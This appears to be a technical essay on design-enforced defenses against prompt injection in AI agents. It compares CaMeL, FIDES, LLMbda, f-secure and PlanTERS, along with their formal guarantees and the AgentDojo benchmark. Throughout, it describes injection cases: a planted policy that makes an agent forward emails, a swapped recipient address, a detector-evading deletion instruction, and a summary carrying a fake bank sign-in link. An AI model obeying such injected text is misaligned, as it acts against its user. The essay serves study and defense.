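# Design-Enforced Defenses Against Prompt Injection: What They Guarantee and What They Assume

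## Prompt injection and the parts of a design-enforced defense

Prompt injection is an attack on software that uses a large language model. An attacker plants instructions in data the system will later read, such as an email, a web page or a shared file, and the model follows them. The attack matters most for AI agents, in which a model can call tools that send messages, move money or open files on a user's behalf. A design-enforced defense protects the system with ordinary software around the model and does not depend on the model detecting the attack. That software typically keeps the component that plans actions away from untrusted text, tracks where each piece of data came from, and checks every tool call against a rule before running it.

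Prompt injection is possible because a language model receives the developer's instructions, the user's request and the contents of a file as one sequence of tokens (words or fragments of words), from which it predicts the next token. *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)*, written by David C for the UK's National Cyber Security Centre in December 2025, contrasts this with SQL injection, an older attack in which someone types database commands into a web form and the database runs them. Programmers learned to stop SQL injection with parameterised queries, which keep the command separate from the user's input so that the database can never run the input as a command. Language models have no such separation. In David C's example, a recruiter's system asks a model to score a CV in which the candidate has hidden an instruction to approve it. He thinks developers may never prevent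 prompt injection as fully as they did SQL injection, and he advises them to limit what the system can do by using deterministic safeguards that contain no language model.

### Why filters and training give no guarantee

Developers first tried to make the model, or a second model beside it, resist hostile text. In *The Attacker Moves Second*, Nasr, Carlini and colleagues (2025) tested twelve such defenses, some against prompt injection and some against jailbreaks, in which the user tries to get around the model's rules. Most of the defenses' developers had reported attack success rates near zero, usually after testing against fixed lists of known attacks or weak automated ones. Nasr and colleagues instead used attacks that adapt to the defense. In one version, a program tries hostile texts on the defended system, scores the responses, keeps the highest-scoring texts and has a language model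 vary them. The adaptive attacks succeeded more than 90 percent of the time against most of the twelve defenses.

None of the approaches withstood attacks adapted to them. Prompt sandwiching repeats the user's request after the untrusted text, and spotlighting uses special markers to set trusted text apart. With these defenses in place, standard attacks succeeded as little as 1 percent of the time, but adapted attacks succeeded more than 95 percent of the time. For Meta SecAlign, a model trained on examples of injection, the success rate rose from 2 percent to 96 percent. Nasr and colleagues also tested four detectors, separate models that scan text for attacks, and beat three of them in over 90 percent of cases and the fourth in 71 percent. One text that got past a detector was worded as a routine company policy requiring staff to log every calendar change by deleting a certain file. A filter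 strict enough to block that text would also block a lot of legitimate mail. Nasr and colleagues still consider detectors useful against unskilled attackers.

Newer models resist prompt injection much better. The Decoder's *Claude Opus 4.5 resists prompt injections better than rivals* reports that, on a benchmark by the security firm Gray Swan, a single strong attack succeeded against Anthropic's Claude Opus 4.5 in 4.7 percent of cases. The success rate rose to 33.6 percent with ten attempts and 63 percent with a hundred. Schneier on Security's *Anthropic’s Opus 5 Is Better at Resisting Prompt Injection* (2026) reports far lower rates for Claude Opus 5, 0.2 percent for one attempt and 2.0 percent within fifteen, compared with 3.1 and 20.0 percent for OpenAI's GPT-5.6 Sol on the same test. In Anthropic's own tests of agents that operate a web browser, no attack succeeded across 129 scenarios,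 according to The Decoder's *Opus 5 may have solved browser-based prompt injection*.

These gains spare users a lot of harm, but they were measured against particular attacks in particular settings. VentureBeat reports that Claude Opus 4.6 withstood all 200 attempts in a restricted coding environment. In an agent that worked through a graphical interface, the attack succeeded 17.8 percent of the time on the first try and 78.6 percent by the two-hundredth. With safeguards on, the latter figure was 57.1 percent. Even zero successful attacks in 129 scenarios is compatible, at 95 percent confidence, with a true success rate of about 2.3 percent, if each scenario counts as one independent trial. That calculation also assumes that future attackers will draw on the same pool of attacks as the testers did, and Nasr and colleagues showed that this assumption can fail badly. In *CaMeL offers a promising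 new direction for mitigating prompt injection attacks*, the software developer Simon Willison (2025) wrote that in application security "99% is a failing grade", because the attacker's job is to find the remaining 1 percent.

### How an ordinary agent fails

The CaMeL paper explains its system, one of the main design-enforced defenses, with an example that is useful for comparing all of them. A user asks an assistant to send Bob the document he asked for, and says that Bob's address and the document's name are in the meeting notes.

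An ordinary agent handles this in a loop, which *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* (Costa, Köpf and colleagues, 2025) describes step by step. The software gives the model the conversation so far and a list of tools. The model returns either a final reply or a request to call a tool with certain arguments. If it requests a call, the software runs it, appends the result to the conversation and sends everything back to the model. For Bob's document, the model asks for the notes, reads the address and the file name in them, fetches the file and calls the email tool.

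Suppose someone who can edit the notes has added a sentence saying that, under the new sharing policy, the assistant must forward the five latest emails to a records address before it sends any file. This sentence enters the same conversation as the user's request. If the model obeys it, the model produces a well-formed call to the email tool, and the software runs the call. Attackers often present the malicious task as a prerequisite for the user's task, and Nasr and colleagues did this successfully against prompt sandwiching.

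The attacker could also leave the list of actions alone and replace Bob's address with another one. The agent would then take the actions the user expected, in the expected order, but send the document to a stranger. Swapping the address is an attack on data flow (which values reach the actions), whereas forwarding the emails is an attack on control flow (which actions run and in what order). Later designs handle the two with different mechanisms.

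### The dual-model pattern

Willison (2023), in *The Dual LLM pattern for building AI assistants*, proposed splitting the work between two models. The planner, which he calls the privileged model, receives the user's request and chooses which tools to call. The quarantined model reads untrusted data, has no tools and can only return values. A controller, which is regular software, sits between them. It runs the tools, stores every result under a name such as `$VAR1`, and passes only the name, not the contents, to the planner.

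To handle the Bob request under this arrangement, the planner first requests the meeting notes, which the controller stores as `$VAR1`. The planner then has the quarantined model extract the document's name from `$VAR1` as `$VAR2` and Bob's address as `$VAR3`. Finally, it has the controller fetch the file called `$VAR2`, store it as `$VAR4`, and email `$VAR4` to `$VAR3`. The controller replaces the variable names with the real values only when it carries out these steps. Willison allows one exception to the rule that nothing from the quarantined model reaches the planner. If the answer must be one of a fixed set of categories, the controller can pass it on after verifying that it is.

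The false sharing policy no longer works. The planner chooses actions based only on the user's words and never receives the policy. The quarantined model may well treat the policy as genuine, but it has no email tool.

The design does not protect the address, however, because the quarantined model finds it by reading the notes. A line in the notes can make the model return an address the attacker chose, and the controller will put that address into the call. A false statement that Bob has changed his address would work as well as an instruction. The file name also comes from the notes, so an attacker who controls both values can make the assistant send a file from the user's drive to an outsider, even though every step of the plan is correct. Willison learned of this flaw in his design from the CaMeL paper two years later.

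Willison called the solution "pretty bad" in 2023 and acknowledged other weak points. If a user pastes hostile text into the request, it goes straight to the planner. Any programming mistake that passes a stored value to the planner breaks the separation. And if the system asks users to approve risky actions, they will learn to click OK as fast as possible.

### CaMeL

CaMeL, short for CApabilities for MachinE Learning, keeps the two models and adds a check on the data. Researchers at Google and ETH Zurich published it in 2025. Its planner reads the user's request and writes a whole program for the task in a restricted form of Python, before any tool has returned anything. For the Bob request, the program would look roughly like this:

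```
notes    = find_meeting_notes("latest")
name     = query_quarantined_llm(f"Which document did Bob ask for? {notes}", str)
address  = query_quarantined_llm(f"What is Bob's address? {notes}", EmailAddress)
document = fetch_document(name)
send_email(recipient=address, attachment=document)
```

A custom interpreter runs this program. *CaMeLoT* (Nikolaou, Eckhoff and colleagues, 2026) describes the interpreter as the component that calls the tools, and the quarantined model as working like one more function in the program. The interpreter attaches a capability to every value, which is a record of where the value came from (its sources) and who may read it (its readers). It also tracks which values derive from which others. In the program above, `address` and `name` both derive from `notes`, so their sources include the notes. An injected sentence that reaches the quarantined model can change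 the contents of `address`, but not its capability.

Before each tool call, such as `send_email`, the interpreter passes the call, its arguments and their recorded capabilities to a policy, a Python function that returns allow or deny with a reason. Willison's example policy always allows reading mail but requires a trusted recipient for sending it. The address in the Bob request came from a file that other people can edit, so the policy does not allow the call outright, and the system can ask the user to approve it.

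This procedure does not detect attacks. Bob's true address comes from the same notes as a forged one would, with the same sources, so the user faces the same question even when nobody has tampered with anything, unless the user's policies already list the address as trusted. A policy can distinguish the two addresses by checking who may read the document. If the company drive lists Bob as a permitted reader, the policy can let the file go to Bob's account and stop it from going anywhere else.

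The split can also improve privacy. The planner must be a strong model because it writes the program, but a small model on the user's own machine could do easier tasks, such as finding an address in a page of notes. The company that hosts the planner would then see the user's request but none of the user's files.

### Labels and how they combine

CaMeL's capabilities are a version of an older idea, information-flow control. It attaches labels to values, carries them through a computation, and blocks any action whose labels break a policy. Each label records how far to trust a value (integrity) and who may read it (confidentiality). The useful part is the rule for combining labels, which two small examples illustrate.

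The simplest integrity labels are trusted and untrusted. A value that depends on anything untrusted is untrusted. If the user dictates the first line of an email and the second line comes from a web page, the whole email is untrusted.

For confidentiality, let each label be the set of people who may read a value. If A, B and C may read one file, and B, C and D may read another, then a summary of both files may go only to people who could have read each of them:

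{A, B, C} ∩ {B, C, D} = {B, C}

Only people who can read both files should be able to read a summary of them. Otherwise A, who can read only the first file, could learn from the summary what the second contains, and D, who can read only the second, could learn what the first contains. Labels can also record who may have written a value, and these sets combine by union. If A, B and C can write to one file and B, C and D to another, all four may have influenced the summary. The operation that combines labels is called the join, written ⊔, and it gives the least restrictive label that still respects every input. A system can carry both kinds of label as a pair and combine each half separately.

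Costa and colleagues apply the rule to tools as well. The result of a tool call takes the combined label of the call, its arguments and everything the tool read. The document that the agent fetches for Bob therefore counts as untrusted even if nobody has tampered with it, because the notes determined which document to fetch. Their two basic policies use these labels. A tool call with real consequences may run only if its label is trusted. A call that sends information out may run only if everyone who can see the channel, such as the recipients of an email, is a permitted reader of that information.

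Under this rule, labels only get stricter, so after enough steps many values are untrusted and few people may read them. Useful systems therefore need deliberate exceptions: endorsement, which treats untrusted data as trusted, and declassification, which treats secret data as public. A user who approves Bob's address by hand is in effect endorsing it.

### FIDES and LLMbda

FIDES, the system that Costa and colleagues built at Microsoft, uses these labels inside an ordinary agent loop. Its planner picks tool calls one at a time, using each result to choose the next, instead of writing a program in advance. But once an untrusted result enters the conversation, everything the model produces afterwards is untrusted, and the policies would then block most useful calls for the rest of the task.

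FIDES borrows its remedy from Willison. When a tool returns a value whose label is stricter than that of the conversation so far, FIDES stores the value in a variable and shows the planner only the variable's name. Values that would not change the conversation's label stay visible. In a list of emails, for example, the planner might see trusted timestamps next to placeholders for subjects and message texts. A quarantined model can process the hidden values and put its answers into new variables. The planner can also inspect a variable, but this lowers the trust in everything that follows. For questions with a yes-or-no answer, a policy may waive part of that reduction.

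For the Bob request, FIDES would hide the text of the notes, have the quarantined model extract the name and the address, and then propose a call to the email tool with variables as arguments. The choice to send an email is trusted because the planner made it without seeing the notes, but the recipient is untrusted. Costa and colleagues describe a policy that requires both the call and the recipient to be trusted but allows untrusted text in the message. This policy would stop Bob's email. They also discuss a looser policy that checks only how the planner arrived at the call, which would let a forged address through. Hiding untrusted text is not sufficient without a policy check. With policies switched off, some attacks in their tests succeeded because the planner could open a variable and follow instructions it found there.

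Garby, Gordon and Sands (2026), in *AI Agents, Conversations, and Information Flow*, see CaMeL and FIDES as combining the same two mechanisms, separate models to protect control flow and information-flow control to protect data flow. Their own system, LLMbda, is a small programming language for writing agents in which every value carries a label. Programmers build the separation into the agent's program themselves, because the language has no built-in pair of models. They can copy a conversation, use the copy to read untrusted content and then discard it, or they can clear a conversation and start again. Garby and colleagues prove a security theorem about every program in the language, whereas CaMeL has no comparable proof and FIDES has proofs for one particular loop.

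### The AgentDojo benchmark

Researchers have tested all three systems on AgentDojo, a set of simulated workplaces for agents. *AgentDojo* (Debenedetti, Zhang and colleagues, 2024) describes four environments: an office workspace with email, calendar and cloud drive, a Slack team chat, a travel agency and a bank. Each contains working tools and dummy data, some of it with slots for an attacker's text. A user task is an ordinary request. One has the same structure as the Bob example, in that the agent must find Dora's address on her website and invite her to Slack. An injection task is an attacker's goal, such as sending a phishing link to a colleague or transferring as much money as possible to a certain account.

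Testers pair every user task with every injection task in the same environment. The first version had 97 user tasks and 27 injection tasks, which gave 629 pairs. Costa and colleagues used 97 user tasks and 36 injection tasks across the four environments, and *Assessing Automated Prompt Injection Attacks in Agentic Environments* (2026) reports more than 900 pairs, so scores from different papers are not always based on the same set of pairs. Fixed code inspects the final state of the simulated mailbox or bank account to determine whether a task succeeded. Debenedetti and colleagues decided against using a language model as the judge because an injection that hijacks the agent might also hijack the judge.

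AgentDojo measures how many user tasks the agent completes without an attack, how many it completes correctly under attack, and how often the attacker's goal is achieved. Its creators meant it as a framework to which others would keep adding attacks adapted to new defenses, and they warned against treating its original attacks as a fixed test. The benchmark doesn't label its data, so anyone who tests a system like FIDES on it must first decide which fields count as untrusted and who may read what.

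### What has to work

If a design-enforced defense is to stop a forged address in the meeting notes, each of the following must hold.

- The planner must turn the request into the right actions, and nothing hostile may reach it. Costa and colleagues treat the user's messages, the system's instructions, the tool descriptions and the models themselves as trusted.
- The labels must be right at the source. If someone marks the shared notes as trusted, the forged address is trusted as well, and every later check will pass it.
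- The policies must cover the argument that matters. A rule for email that examines the recipient and ignores the attachment still lets the notes decide which file Bob receives.
- The interpreter, or the loop that takes its place in FIDES, must carry the labels through every operation without dropping one, and no tool call may bypass it.
- The person who receives a request for approval must look at the address and know whether it is Bob's.
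- There must be no side channels, meaning observable effects outside the tracked data, such as the timing of a run, its error messages or the number of calls it makes. An attacker who can watch these may learn something about a document that the system never sends.

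## What is proved, and under which premises

A security theorem about an agent starts from premises much like those listed above and proves a property that holds in every run, whatever text an attacker writes. The property differs from system to system. Some of these properties rule out Bob's forged address, while others still hold when the document goes to a stranger.

### The FIDES loop and its two policies

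Costa and colleagues assume that the user, the models and the tool descriptions are trustworthy. Their attacker can tamper with data that tools fetch from untrusted sources and can observe the effects of some tool calls, but cannot see the traffic between the software and the model. Even a read-only tool can leak information to this attacker, because a web search, for example, may show up in a site's visitor statistics.

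The FIDES loop keeps a label on every message, tool call, argument and stored value. One round runs as follows.

1. The loop sends the conversation and the list of tools to the planner. It gives the planner's response the combined label of everything it sent, because nobody can tell exactly which parts of its input a model used.
2. If the response is a tool call, the loop replaces any variable names in the arguments with the stored values, which keep their own labels. A trusted call can therefore have an untrusted argument.
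3. The loop checks the call against the policies. If the check fails, the call does not run. In the formal description the whole run then ends, whereas the tested software reports the refusal to the planner, which may try something else.
4. If the check succeeds, the tool runs. Its result, and any stored data it may have changed, get the combined label of the call, its arguments and everything the tool may have read.
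5. The loop hides any part of the result with a stricter label than the conversation's and starts the next round. When the planner writes a final reply, the loop hands it to the user with its label and checks no policy.

The previous section gave the two basic policies in words. In symbols, let ℓ be the label of the call, ℓ₁ to ℓₙ the labels of its arguments, and (T, _) any label that is trusted, whatever its confidentiality. The policy for consequential actions allows a call only if

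ℓ ⊔ ℓ₁ ⊔ … ⊔ ℓₙ = (T, _)

The confidentiality policy applies to any argument that a tool sends out. If S is the set of people who may read the argument and R is the set of people who can see the channel, the call may run only if

R ⊆ S

Under the confidentiality policy alone, an injected sentence could still trigger an email, but only to people who may already read the email's contents. The policy for consequential actions, used alone, stops untrusted text from triggering the email but lets a trusted call send a secret to an outsider, on the assumption that the user meant it to. Costa and colleagues get their strongest protection by requiring both policies. Bob's forged address then fails the trust check because it came from the notes. It also fails the confidentiality check if the stranger is not permitted to read the document.

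In their tests, Costa and colleagues used looser versions of the rules. Their rule for consequential actions checked only the label of the call, not the labels of its arguments. They extended the confidentiality rule to block outgoing messages that contain untrusted links. The email tool could run if the call passed either rule. Since the planner's call to the email tool is trusted, the tool could send a document to a forged address even if the recipient had no right to read it. The tool for sending money checked only the label of the call, so it would also accept an account number from a tampered bill if the planner had passed the number as a variable. Two organisations running the same FIDES code could therefore get different protection if they load different rules.

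### Explicit secrecy

Costa and colleagues claim that the loop satisfies explicit secrecy, a formal property they take from earlier research on tracking data through ordinary programs. This property covers only confidentiality. For integrity, FIDES offers the policy check itself, which blocks any consequential call whose label doesn't pass.

Every run makes a series of tool calls, and together these calls transform the stored data, such as files, mailboxes and chat channels. Let g be that transformation. Some storage locations are public and the rest are secret. Two versions of the stored data, d₁ and d₂, are low-equivalent, written d₁ =_L d₂, if they agree on every public location. The agent satisfies explicit secrecy if, for every run that starts from some d₁ and performs g,

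g(d₁) =_L g(d₂) for every d₂ with d₁ =_L d₂

Replaying the same calls on data with different secrets must leave the public locations with the same contents. Costa and colleagues also give an equivalent definition, in which an attacker who watches the public locations change must not be able to rule out any secret that was possible at the start.

Suppose a tool copies a salary file into a public folder. Replaying the copy with a different salary puts different contents in the folder, so the run violates explicit secrecy. Now suppose the agent reads the salary and posts "ready" in a public channel only if the salary is above 100,000. Replaying that post with a different salary gives the same result, so the run satisfies explicit secrecy, even though anyone in the channel who knows the rule has learned something about the salary. Explicit secrecy does not rule out this kind of leak, called an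 implicit flow, because it covers only the calls the agent made, not the calls it would have made with a different salary.

The written definition also has a gap because it treats the conversation and the hidden variables as part of the program, not as stored data. If a tool returns the salary into the conversation and the planner copies it into a public message, the salary is a fixed argument inside g, and a replay on other data would post the same number. Taken literally, explicit secrecy therefore permits this leak. The mechanism still stops it, because the loop carries the secret label from the tool's result to the argument and the confidentiality policy then blocks the message.

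Costa and colleagues state that the loop can enforce explicit secrecy, but they don't print a proof. Their appendix contains the definitions and one lemma, showing that applying g to the starting data gives the data at the end of the run. Garby and colleagues therefore credit FIDES with more than the paper shows when they attribute a noninterference theorem for the loop to it. The definitions also assume a deterministic model, one that always gives the same response to the same input, whereas the output of commercial models is usually partly random. Costa and colleagues also leave out timing and the length of network packets.

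### Why they did not use noninterference

Noninterference is stricter than explicit secrecy. It requires that changing the secrets change nothing an outsider can see, including which calls the agent makes. Costa and colleagues argue that to enforce it, a system would essentially have to forbid any tool that may write to a public place once any tool has read something secret. An assistant that had read a private calendar could not email an outsider for the rest of the task, even to write "thank you". Explicit secrecy permits that email, and phone and browser software has long relied on the same compromise.

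*On the Relative Security of Prompt Injection* (Dongol, 2026) gives another reason. A calendar assistant that answers meeting requests has to reveal when its user is free. Because its replies depend on private data, it violates noninterference even when nobody attacks it.

Garby and colleagues object that explicit secrecy is weakest where data and control are interchangeable, as in an agent that writes its own programs. Such a program can test a secret one character at a time and take a different branch for each possible answer. This leaks the whole secret rather than a single hint about a salary, and explicit secrecy permits it. Settling for explicit secrecy is easier to defend for a fixed loop with a few tools than for an agent that runs any code its planner produces.

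### Noninterference in LLMbda

LLMbda tracks branches as well as values. While a program is inside a branch that depends on a secret, the interpreter labels the branch itself secret, and everything the program computes there inherits that label. In one of Garby and colleagues' examples, a program tries to add a message to a public conversation from inside such a branch. The interpreter stops the program, because an observer could otherwise learn the secret from whether the message was there.

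The theorem establishes termination-insensitive probabilistic noninterference (TIPNI). "Probabilistic" means it covers models whose responses vary randomly. "Termination-insensitive" means it allows one kind of leak, through whether a run finishes. A run counts as unfinished if it loops forever or if a failed label check stops it.

To define it, pick an observer at level m, who can see every value whose label is m or lower in the ordering and no others. Two programs are indistinguishable to this observer, written e₀ ~ₘ e₁, if they differ only inside values the observer cannot see. The same relation applies to conversations, C₀ ~ₘ C₁. Each starting point gives every visible outcome q a probability. These may sum to less than 1, and the remainder is the chance that the run does not finish. Two such sets of probabilities, P₀ and P₁, are compatible, written P₀ ⌣ P₁, if there is some Q with

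P₀(q) ≤ Q(q) and P₁(q) ≤ Q(q) for every outcome q, and Σ Q(q) ≤ 1

The property is then

TIPNI(m): if C₀ ~ₘ C₁ and e₀ ~ₘ e₁, then ⟦pc ⊢ C₀, e₀⟧ₘ ⌣ ⟦pc ⊢ C₁, e₁⟧ₘ

Here ⟦…⟧ₘ stands for the probabilities of the outcomes as the observer sees them, and pc is the label of the current branch.

For example, a program might toss a coin and report the result, but hang on tails if a secret bit is 1. If the bit is 0, the observer sees heads or tails, each with probability one half. If the bit is 1, the observer sees heads with probability one half and otherwise nothing. A Q that gives one half to each result covers both cases and sums to 1, so the two are compatible and TIPNI allows the program. A program that printed the bit would fail, because Q would have to give probability 1 to both "0" and "1", for a total of 2 rather than 1.

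Garby and colleagues first tried a definition that compares only the runs that finish, but concluded that it was wrong. In the coin program, every finished run reports heads when the bit is 1, so that definition would have rejected the program even though its only leak is through hanging. For programs that always finish, compatible probabilities must be equal, and TIPNI becomes ordinary probabilistic noninterference. For other programs, the chance that runs do not finish limits how far the two sets can differ.

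The first theorem states that TIPNI(m) holds for every m and every program without endorsement, including programs in which the model writes code that the interpreter then runs. TIPNI(m) means that secrets cannot affect what an observer sees if that observer sees only public values, and that untrusted text cannot affect what an observer sees if that observer sees only trusted values.

To construct Q, Garby and colleagues define a second way to run a program, which skips any step as soon as its label rises above m and substitutes a dummy value. Every visible outcome is at least as probable in this version as in the real one. This version also behaves identically for any two starting points that the observer cannot distinguish, since it skips exactly the parts in which they differ. Its probabilities can therefore serve as Q for both. Lean, a proof checker, has verified every step of the proof.

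### Endorsement without leaking secrets

In an example from Garby and colleagues, a quarantined model sorts an incoming email into one of a few categories, and the agent puts the category in the subject line of its reply. The category is untrusted because it comes from the email, but the tool that sends replies accepts only trusted text. The program therefore checks that the category is one of the allowed ones and then endorses it, which marks it as trusted. After that, the theorem no longer guarantees that untrusted text has no effect on trusted results.

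Insulated TIPNI is the guarantee that still holds after endorsement. In LLMbda, endorsement may change only the integrity half of a label. Relabelling a value from untrusted to trusted therefore makes no difference to what an observer can see if that observer can see values at any level of trust but is barred from secrets. In their second theorem, Garby and colleagues prove that TIPNI(m) holds for every such observer, however the attacker chooses the untrusted inputs and whatever the program endorses. If the email category depended on a secret, it would still carry a secret label after endorsement, and a check on that label would still catch it.

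The theorem does not guarantee that endorsed data is harmless. A program can endorse the address in the meeting notes, and a forged address then passes the trust check. The email tool then sends the document to that address unless it also checks who may read the document.

Neither theorem assumes anything about the model's honesty. Garby and colleagues conclude that, in a program without endorsement, even a fully compromised model can do no more than the trusted tools allow. The theorems do assume that the programmer who writes the tools labels incoming data correctly and checks labels wherever a tool does something sensitive. All data sources must also be part of the program, which Garby and colleagues acknowledge is a simplification, since real tools communicate with outside services. The model's response must depend only on the current conversation, because a model that remembered other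 conversations could carry text past the separation. Finally, someone has to decide which part of each label counts as integrity. If the whole label counted, endorsement could change any label and the second theorem would guarantee nothing.

### CaMeL and fixed architectures

CaMeL lacks such a theorem partly because its planner writes a new program for every request. A proof would have to cover every program the planner could write, which requires a mathematical definition of what each one does. The only complete definition is the interpreter's Python code. According to Garby and colleagues, CaMeL's creators call formalisation a "crucial direction" for later work. Garby and colleagues also found programs on which the interpreter loses a label, so a noninterference theorem about the code they examined would be false.

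An earlier system does have a proof, for a much simpler structure. *System-Level Defense against Indirect Prompt Injection Attacks* (Wu, Cecchetti and Xiao, 2024) describes f-secure, in which a planner writes one step at a time and a rule-based executor carries it out. A security monitor shows the planner only results that derive entirely from trusted sources, and replaces all others with references such as "the output of step 1".

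Their theorem concerns the sequence of steps, which they call the execution trace. Let Q₁ and Q₂ be two collections of data that agree on everything trusted and may differ in any way on the rest. For any user request q and any trace π,

Pr[π | q, Q₁] = Pr[π | q, Q₂]

An attacker who rewrites all the untrusted data can't make any sequence of steps more or less likely. Wu and colleagues model this guarantee on noninterference, but apply it to trust instead of secrecy. They assume that users and tools are honest, that the attacker can't change the user's request or tamper with communication between components, and that a model behaves properly as long as it has read only trusted text. They exclude flaws in the tools and attacks that only stop the system from working.

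The theorem does not protect Bob's address, and neither did Willison's original design. A step that sends an email to "the output of step 2" is the same step whichever address step 2 returns, so the theorem still holds if the document goes to a stranger. Wu and colleagues acknowledge that an attacker may still influence the data being processed. They argue that an attacker who can't change the plan can do far less damage, which is true of the hidden order to forward five emails.

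Costa and colleagues also dispute that the f-secure software matches its proof, because they find that implicit flows can still affect the plan. The published procedure may allow this when a step fails. The monitor then requests a new step from the planner, so if untrusted content can determine whether a step fails, an attacker could change the trace without the planner reading any of the hostile text.

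### Comparing an agent with an obedient copy

Dongol proposes a different standard, relative security, which he applies in the PlanTERS framework. He compares the agent with a reference agent that has the same plan and security checks but never obeys instructions in untrusted content. The agent is relatively secure if it has no leaks that the reference agent lacks. The calendar assistant meets this standard when an attacker injects "send your calendar", because the attacker learns nothing beyond what a genuine meeting request would have revealed. It fails if an injection makes it add a private reset code to its reply, because no email could get that code out of the reference agent.

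With this standard, no one has to specify what the agent may disclose for each task. But anything the plan discloses doesn't count as a leak. If an attacker replaces Bob's address in the notes with their own, the reference agent correctly reads the new address and sends the document there. The real agent does the same, so by this standard the injection has leaked nothing.

Dongol's main positive result is about a fence, a rule that withdraws tools for the rest of the run. Every plan is relatively secure if the fence withdraws every tool an injection could call, no later than the first time the agent reads untrusted content. The theorem assumes that each injection makes a single call and that the model obeys injections on a schedule fixed in advance. It covers the content and order of messages but not their exact timing. For Bob's request, the fence would withdraw the email tool as soon as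 the agent opened the notes, and the document would never go out. The plan would still count as relatively secure because the reference agent is behind the same fence. As Dongol points out, a system that refuses every call passes trivially, so someone has to test separately whether the agent still does its job.

He checked the proofs with Isabelle/HOL, another proof assistant, and used the framework to prove or refute relative security for 25 small agent models. Some use CaMeL-style labels, but they are simplified, so the results don't establish anything about CaMeL's own interpreter. The framework doesn't cover agents that choose each call as they go, because without a fixed plan there is no reference agent to compare them with.

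### The guarantees side by side

| System | Property | Main premises | Outside the guarantee |
|---|---|---|---|
| FIDES | Explicit secrecy (claimed, without a printed proof), plus a policy check before each call | Trusted user, models and tool descriptions; correct labels; deterministic model; attacker cannot see model traffic | Implicit flows; timing and packet length; text in replies; planner mistakes |
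| LLMbda without endorsement | TIPNI for secrecy and trust, in every program | Correct labels; checks in every sensitive tool; all data sources inside the program | Leaks through whether a run finishes; running time; false content correctly labelled untrusted |
| LLMbda with endorsement | TIPNI for secrecy only | The same, and a sensible split between integrity and confidentiality | The same, and harm done by endorsed data |
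| f-secure | Untrusted data cannot change the probability of any sequence of steps | Honest users and tools; correct labels; models reliable on trusted text | Changed values inside a step; flaws in tools; attacks on availability |
| PlanTERS | No leak that the reference agent lacks | Trusted plan and monitor; for the fence theorem, single-call injections on a fixed schedule | Harmful actions that leak nothing; side channels; planner mistakes; poisoned tools |
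| CaMeL | No theorem; policy check before each call | Correct interpreter, labels, policies and plan | Cases where the user tells the agent to follow a document |

### Attacks that only change text

A text-to-text attack alters what the model writes without changing which tools run or leaking anything secret. For example, one of AgentDojo's injection tasks tries to make a travel assistant tell the user that a certain hotel is gorgeous and well worth a visit. Costa and colleagues state that FIDES doesn't protect against such attacks, and they exclude them from their count of successful injections.

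The same method can do more harm than a hotel advertisement. If a user asks whether any email from the landlord needs an answer, a line in one email could make the quarantined model omit that email from the summary. An injected line could also make the summary say that the user's bank has locked their account and include a sign-in link. If the user follows the link and enters a password, the user's own browser sends it, and FIDES's labels and policies don't apply there. In FIDES's tests, the ban on untrusted links covered messages the agent sent but not its reply to the user.

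Noninterference doesn't rule out the false summary either. It prevents untrusted inputs from affecting trusted outputs, but a summary of an untrusted email is labeled an untrusted output.

Costa and colleagues suggest that the system could either mark untrusted passages on the screen or refuse to show them. They expect refusing to make the system considerably less useful, and an assistant that refused would be useless for reading email. Marking preserves more of the system's usefulness but protects only a user who heeds the mark. It also can't distinguish a false summary from a true one, because both come from the same email.

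When the agent sends the altered text to another person, the text becomes an argument of a tool call, so a policy can apply to it. In one of Costa and colleagues' examples, the agent summarises three emails and sends the summary to a colleague on Slack. An instruction in one email can make the summary empty. A policy that requires trusted arguments would block this message, but it would also block a summary that no injection had altered.

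Some users give the attacker more room by asking the agent to follow whatever instructions a document contains. In an AgentDojo banking task, the user asks the agent to make the payment described in a file, and the attacker replaces the file's contents with a different payment. Garby and colleagues' agent made the attacker's payment in two runs, after endorsing the file's contents. Without endorsement, the system blocks the attacker's payment but would also block the real bill. CaMeL's threat model excludes this case. Labels can establish that the payment instruction came from the file the user named, but not that the bill is genuine.

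### Honest mistakes

The planner can also cause harm without an attack. Costa and colleagues note that a model may misread the user's intention or make unnecessary tool calls even when all the data is trusted, and that the consequences may resemble those of an attack.

In one test of FIDES, a user asked the agent to change a bank password if it noticed a suspicious transaction. FIDES showed the planner the trusted dates and amounts but hid the untrusted descriptions. The planner flagged a large payment as suspicious and changed the password without reading the description. Every label was correct, and the policy allowed the call because nothing untrusted had influenced it. AgentDojo counted the task as completed. But the payment might have been an ordinary one, such as rent, which the planner could not rule out without the description.

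Hiding data from a planner can encourage this kind of guess. In another banking task, the user asked what a New Year's gift had cost. A simpler planner in the same study, which could not read the hidden descriptions, found one transaction dated 1 January and reported its amount, though the payment could just as easily have been for groceries. Neither guess breaks an information-flow rule, because labels don't record whether the planner drew the right conclusion from a value. Dongol lists the planner's correctness as outside his framework. Wu and colleagues assume that a model can be trusted with trusted text, but their theorem needs this only in the sense that nobody has manipulated the model.

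### Is this "secure by design"?

Adaptive attacks search for wording that gets past a filter or a trained model, but no wording can influence a planner that never receives the text. Wu and colleagues treat the model as a black box and assume that any untrusted input could take it over completely. Their argument therefore doesn't need revising for each new model, and no filter has comparable support.

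But each theorem secures only the property it states, and CaMeL, whose paper has "by design" in its title, has no theorem. A buyer can learn more by asking how well a design prevents a particular harm. All these designs defend well against the order to forward five emails, because the planner either never reads the order or loses the email tool when it does. In the case of Bob's address, protection depends on whether the email policy checks the recipient. If a summary tells the user to sign in at a fake bank site, the design can do no more than label the text.

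## The planner and the inputs it trusts

CaMeL and FIDES keep tool results away from the planner, but the planner still reads the user's request, the descriptions of the tools it can call and, when several agents work together, messages from other agents. An attacker who can write into any of these can get actions into the plan, and the rest of the system will treat those actions as the user's own wishes. Even when all the inputs are clean, the planner can write a plan that lets untrusted data choose the next action.

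### The user's request

Tallam and Miller (2025), in *Operationalizing CaMeL*, point out that CaMeL assumes the user's first message is benign. FIDES and *Architecting Secure AI Agents* (Xiang, Zagieboylo and colleagues, 2026), a position paper led by NVIDIA researchers, make the same assumption. This is reasonable for words the user types, since the agent exists to do what the user wants. But users also paste text. If someone pastes an email from Bob into the chat and adds "please deal with this", the planner reads the whole email as part of the request. Labels do not help here, because the email is trusted along with the rest of the request, and so is any address the planner copies from it.

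There is little evidence on how often attackers exploit this. Tallam and Miller claim that corporate red teams, testing their own companies' systems, have planted lasting instructions in a planner with a single crafted prompt. They cite no report of such an exercise, only research on how often people click phishing links. Still, a planner that reads a pasted email is exposed to the same attack as an ordinary agent that reads one, and ordinary agents do obey instructions planted in emails.

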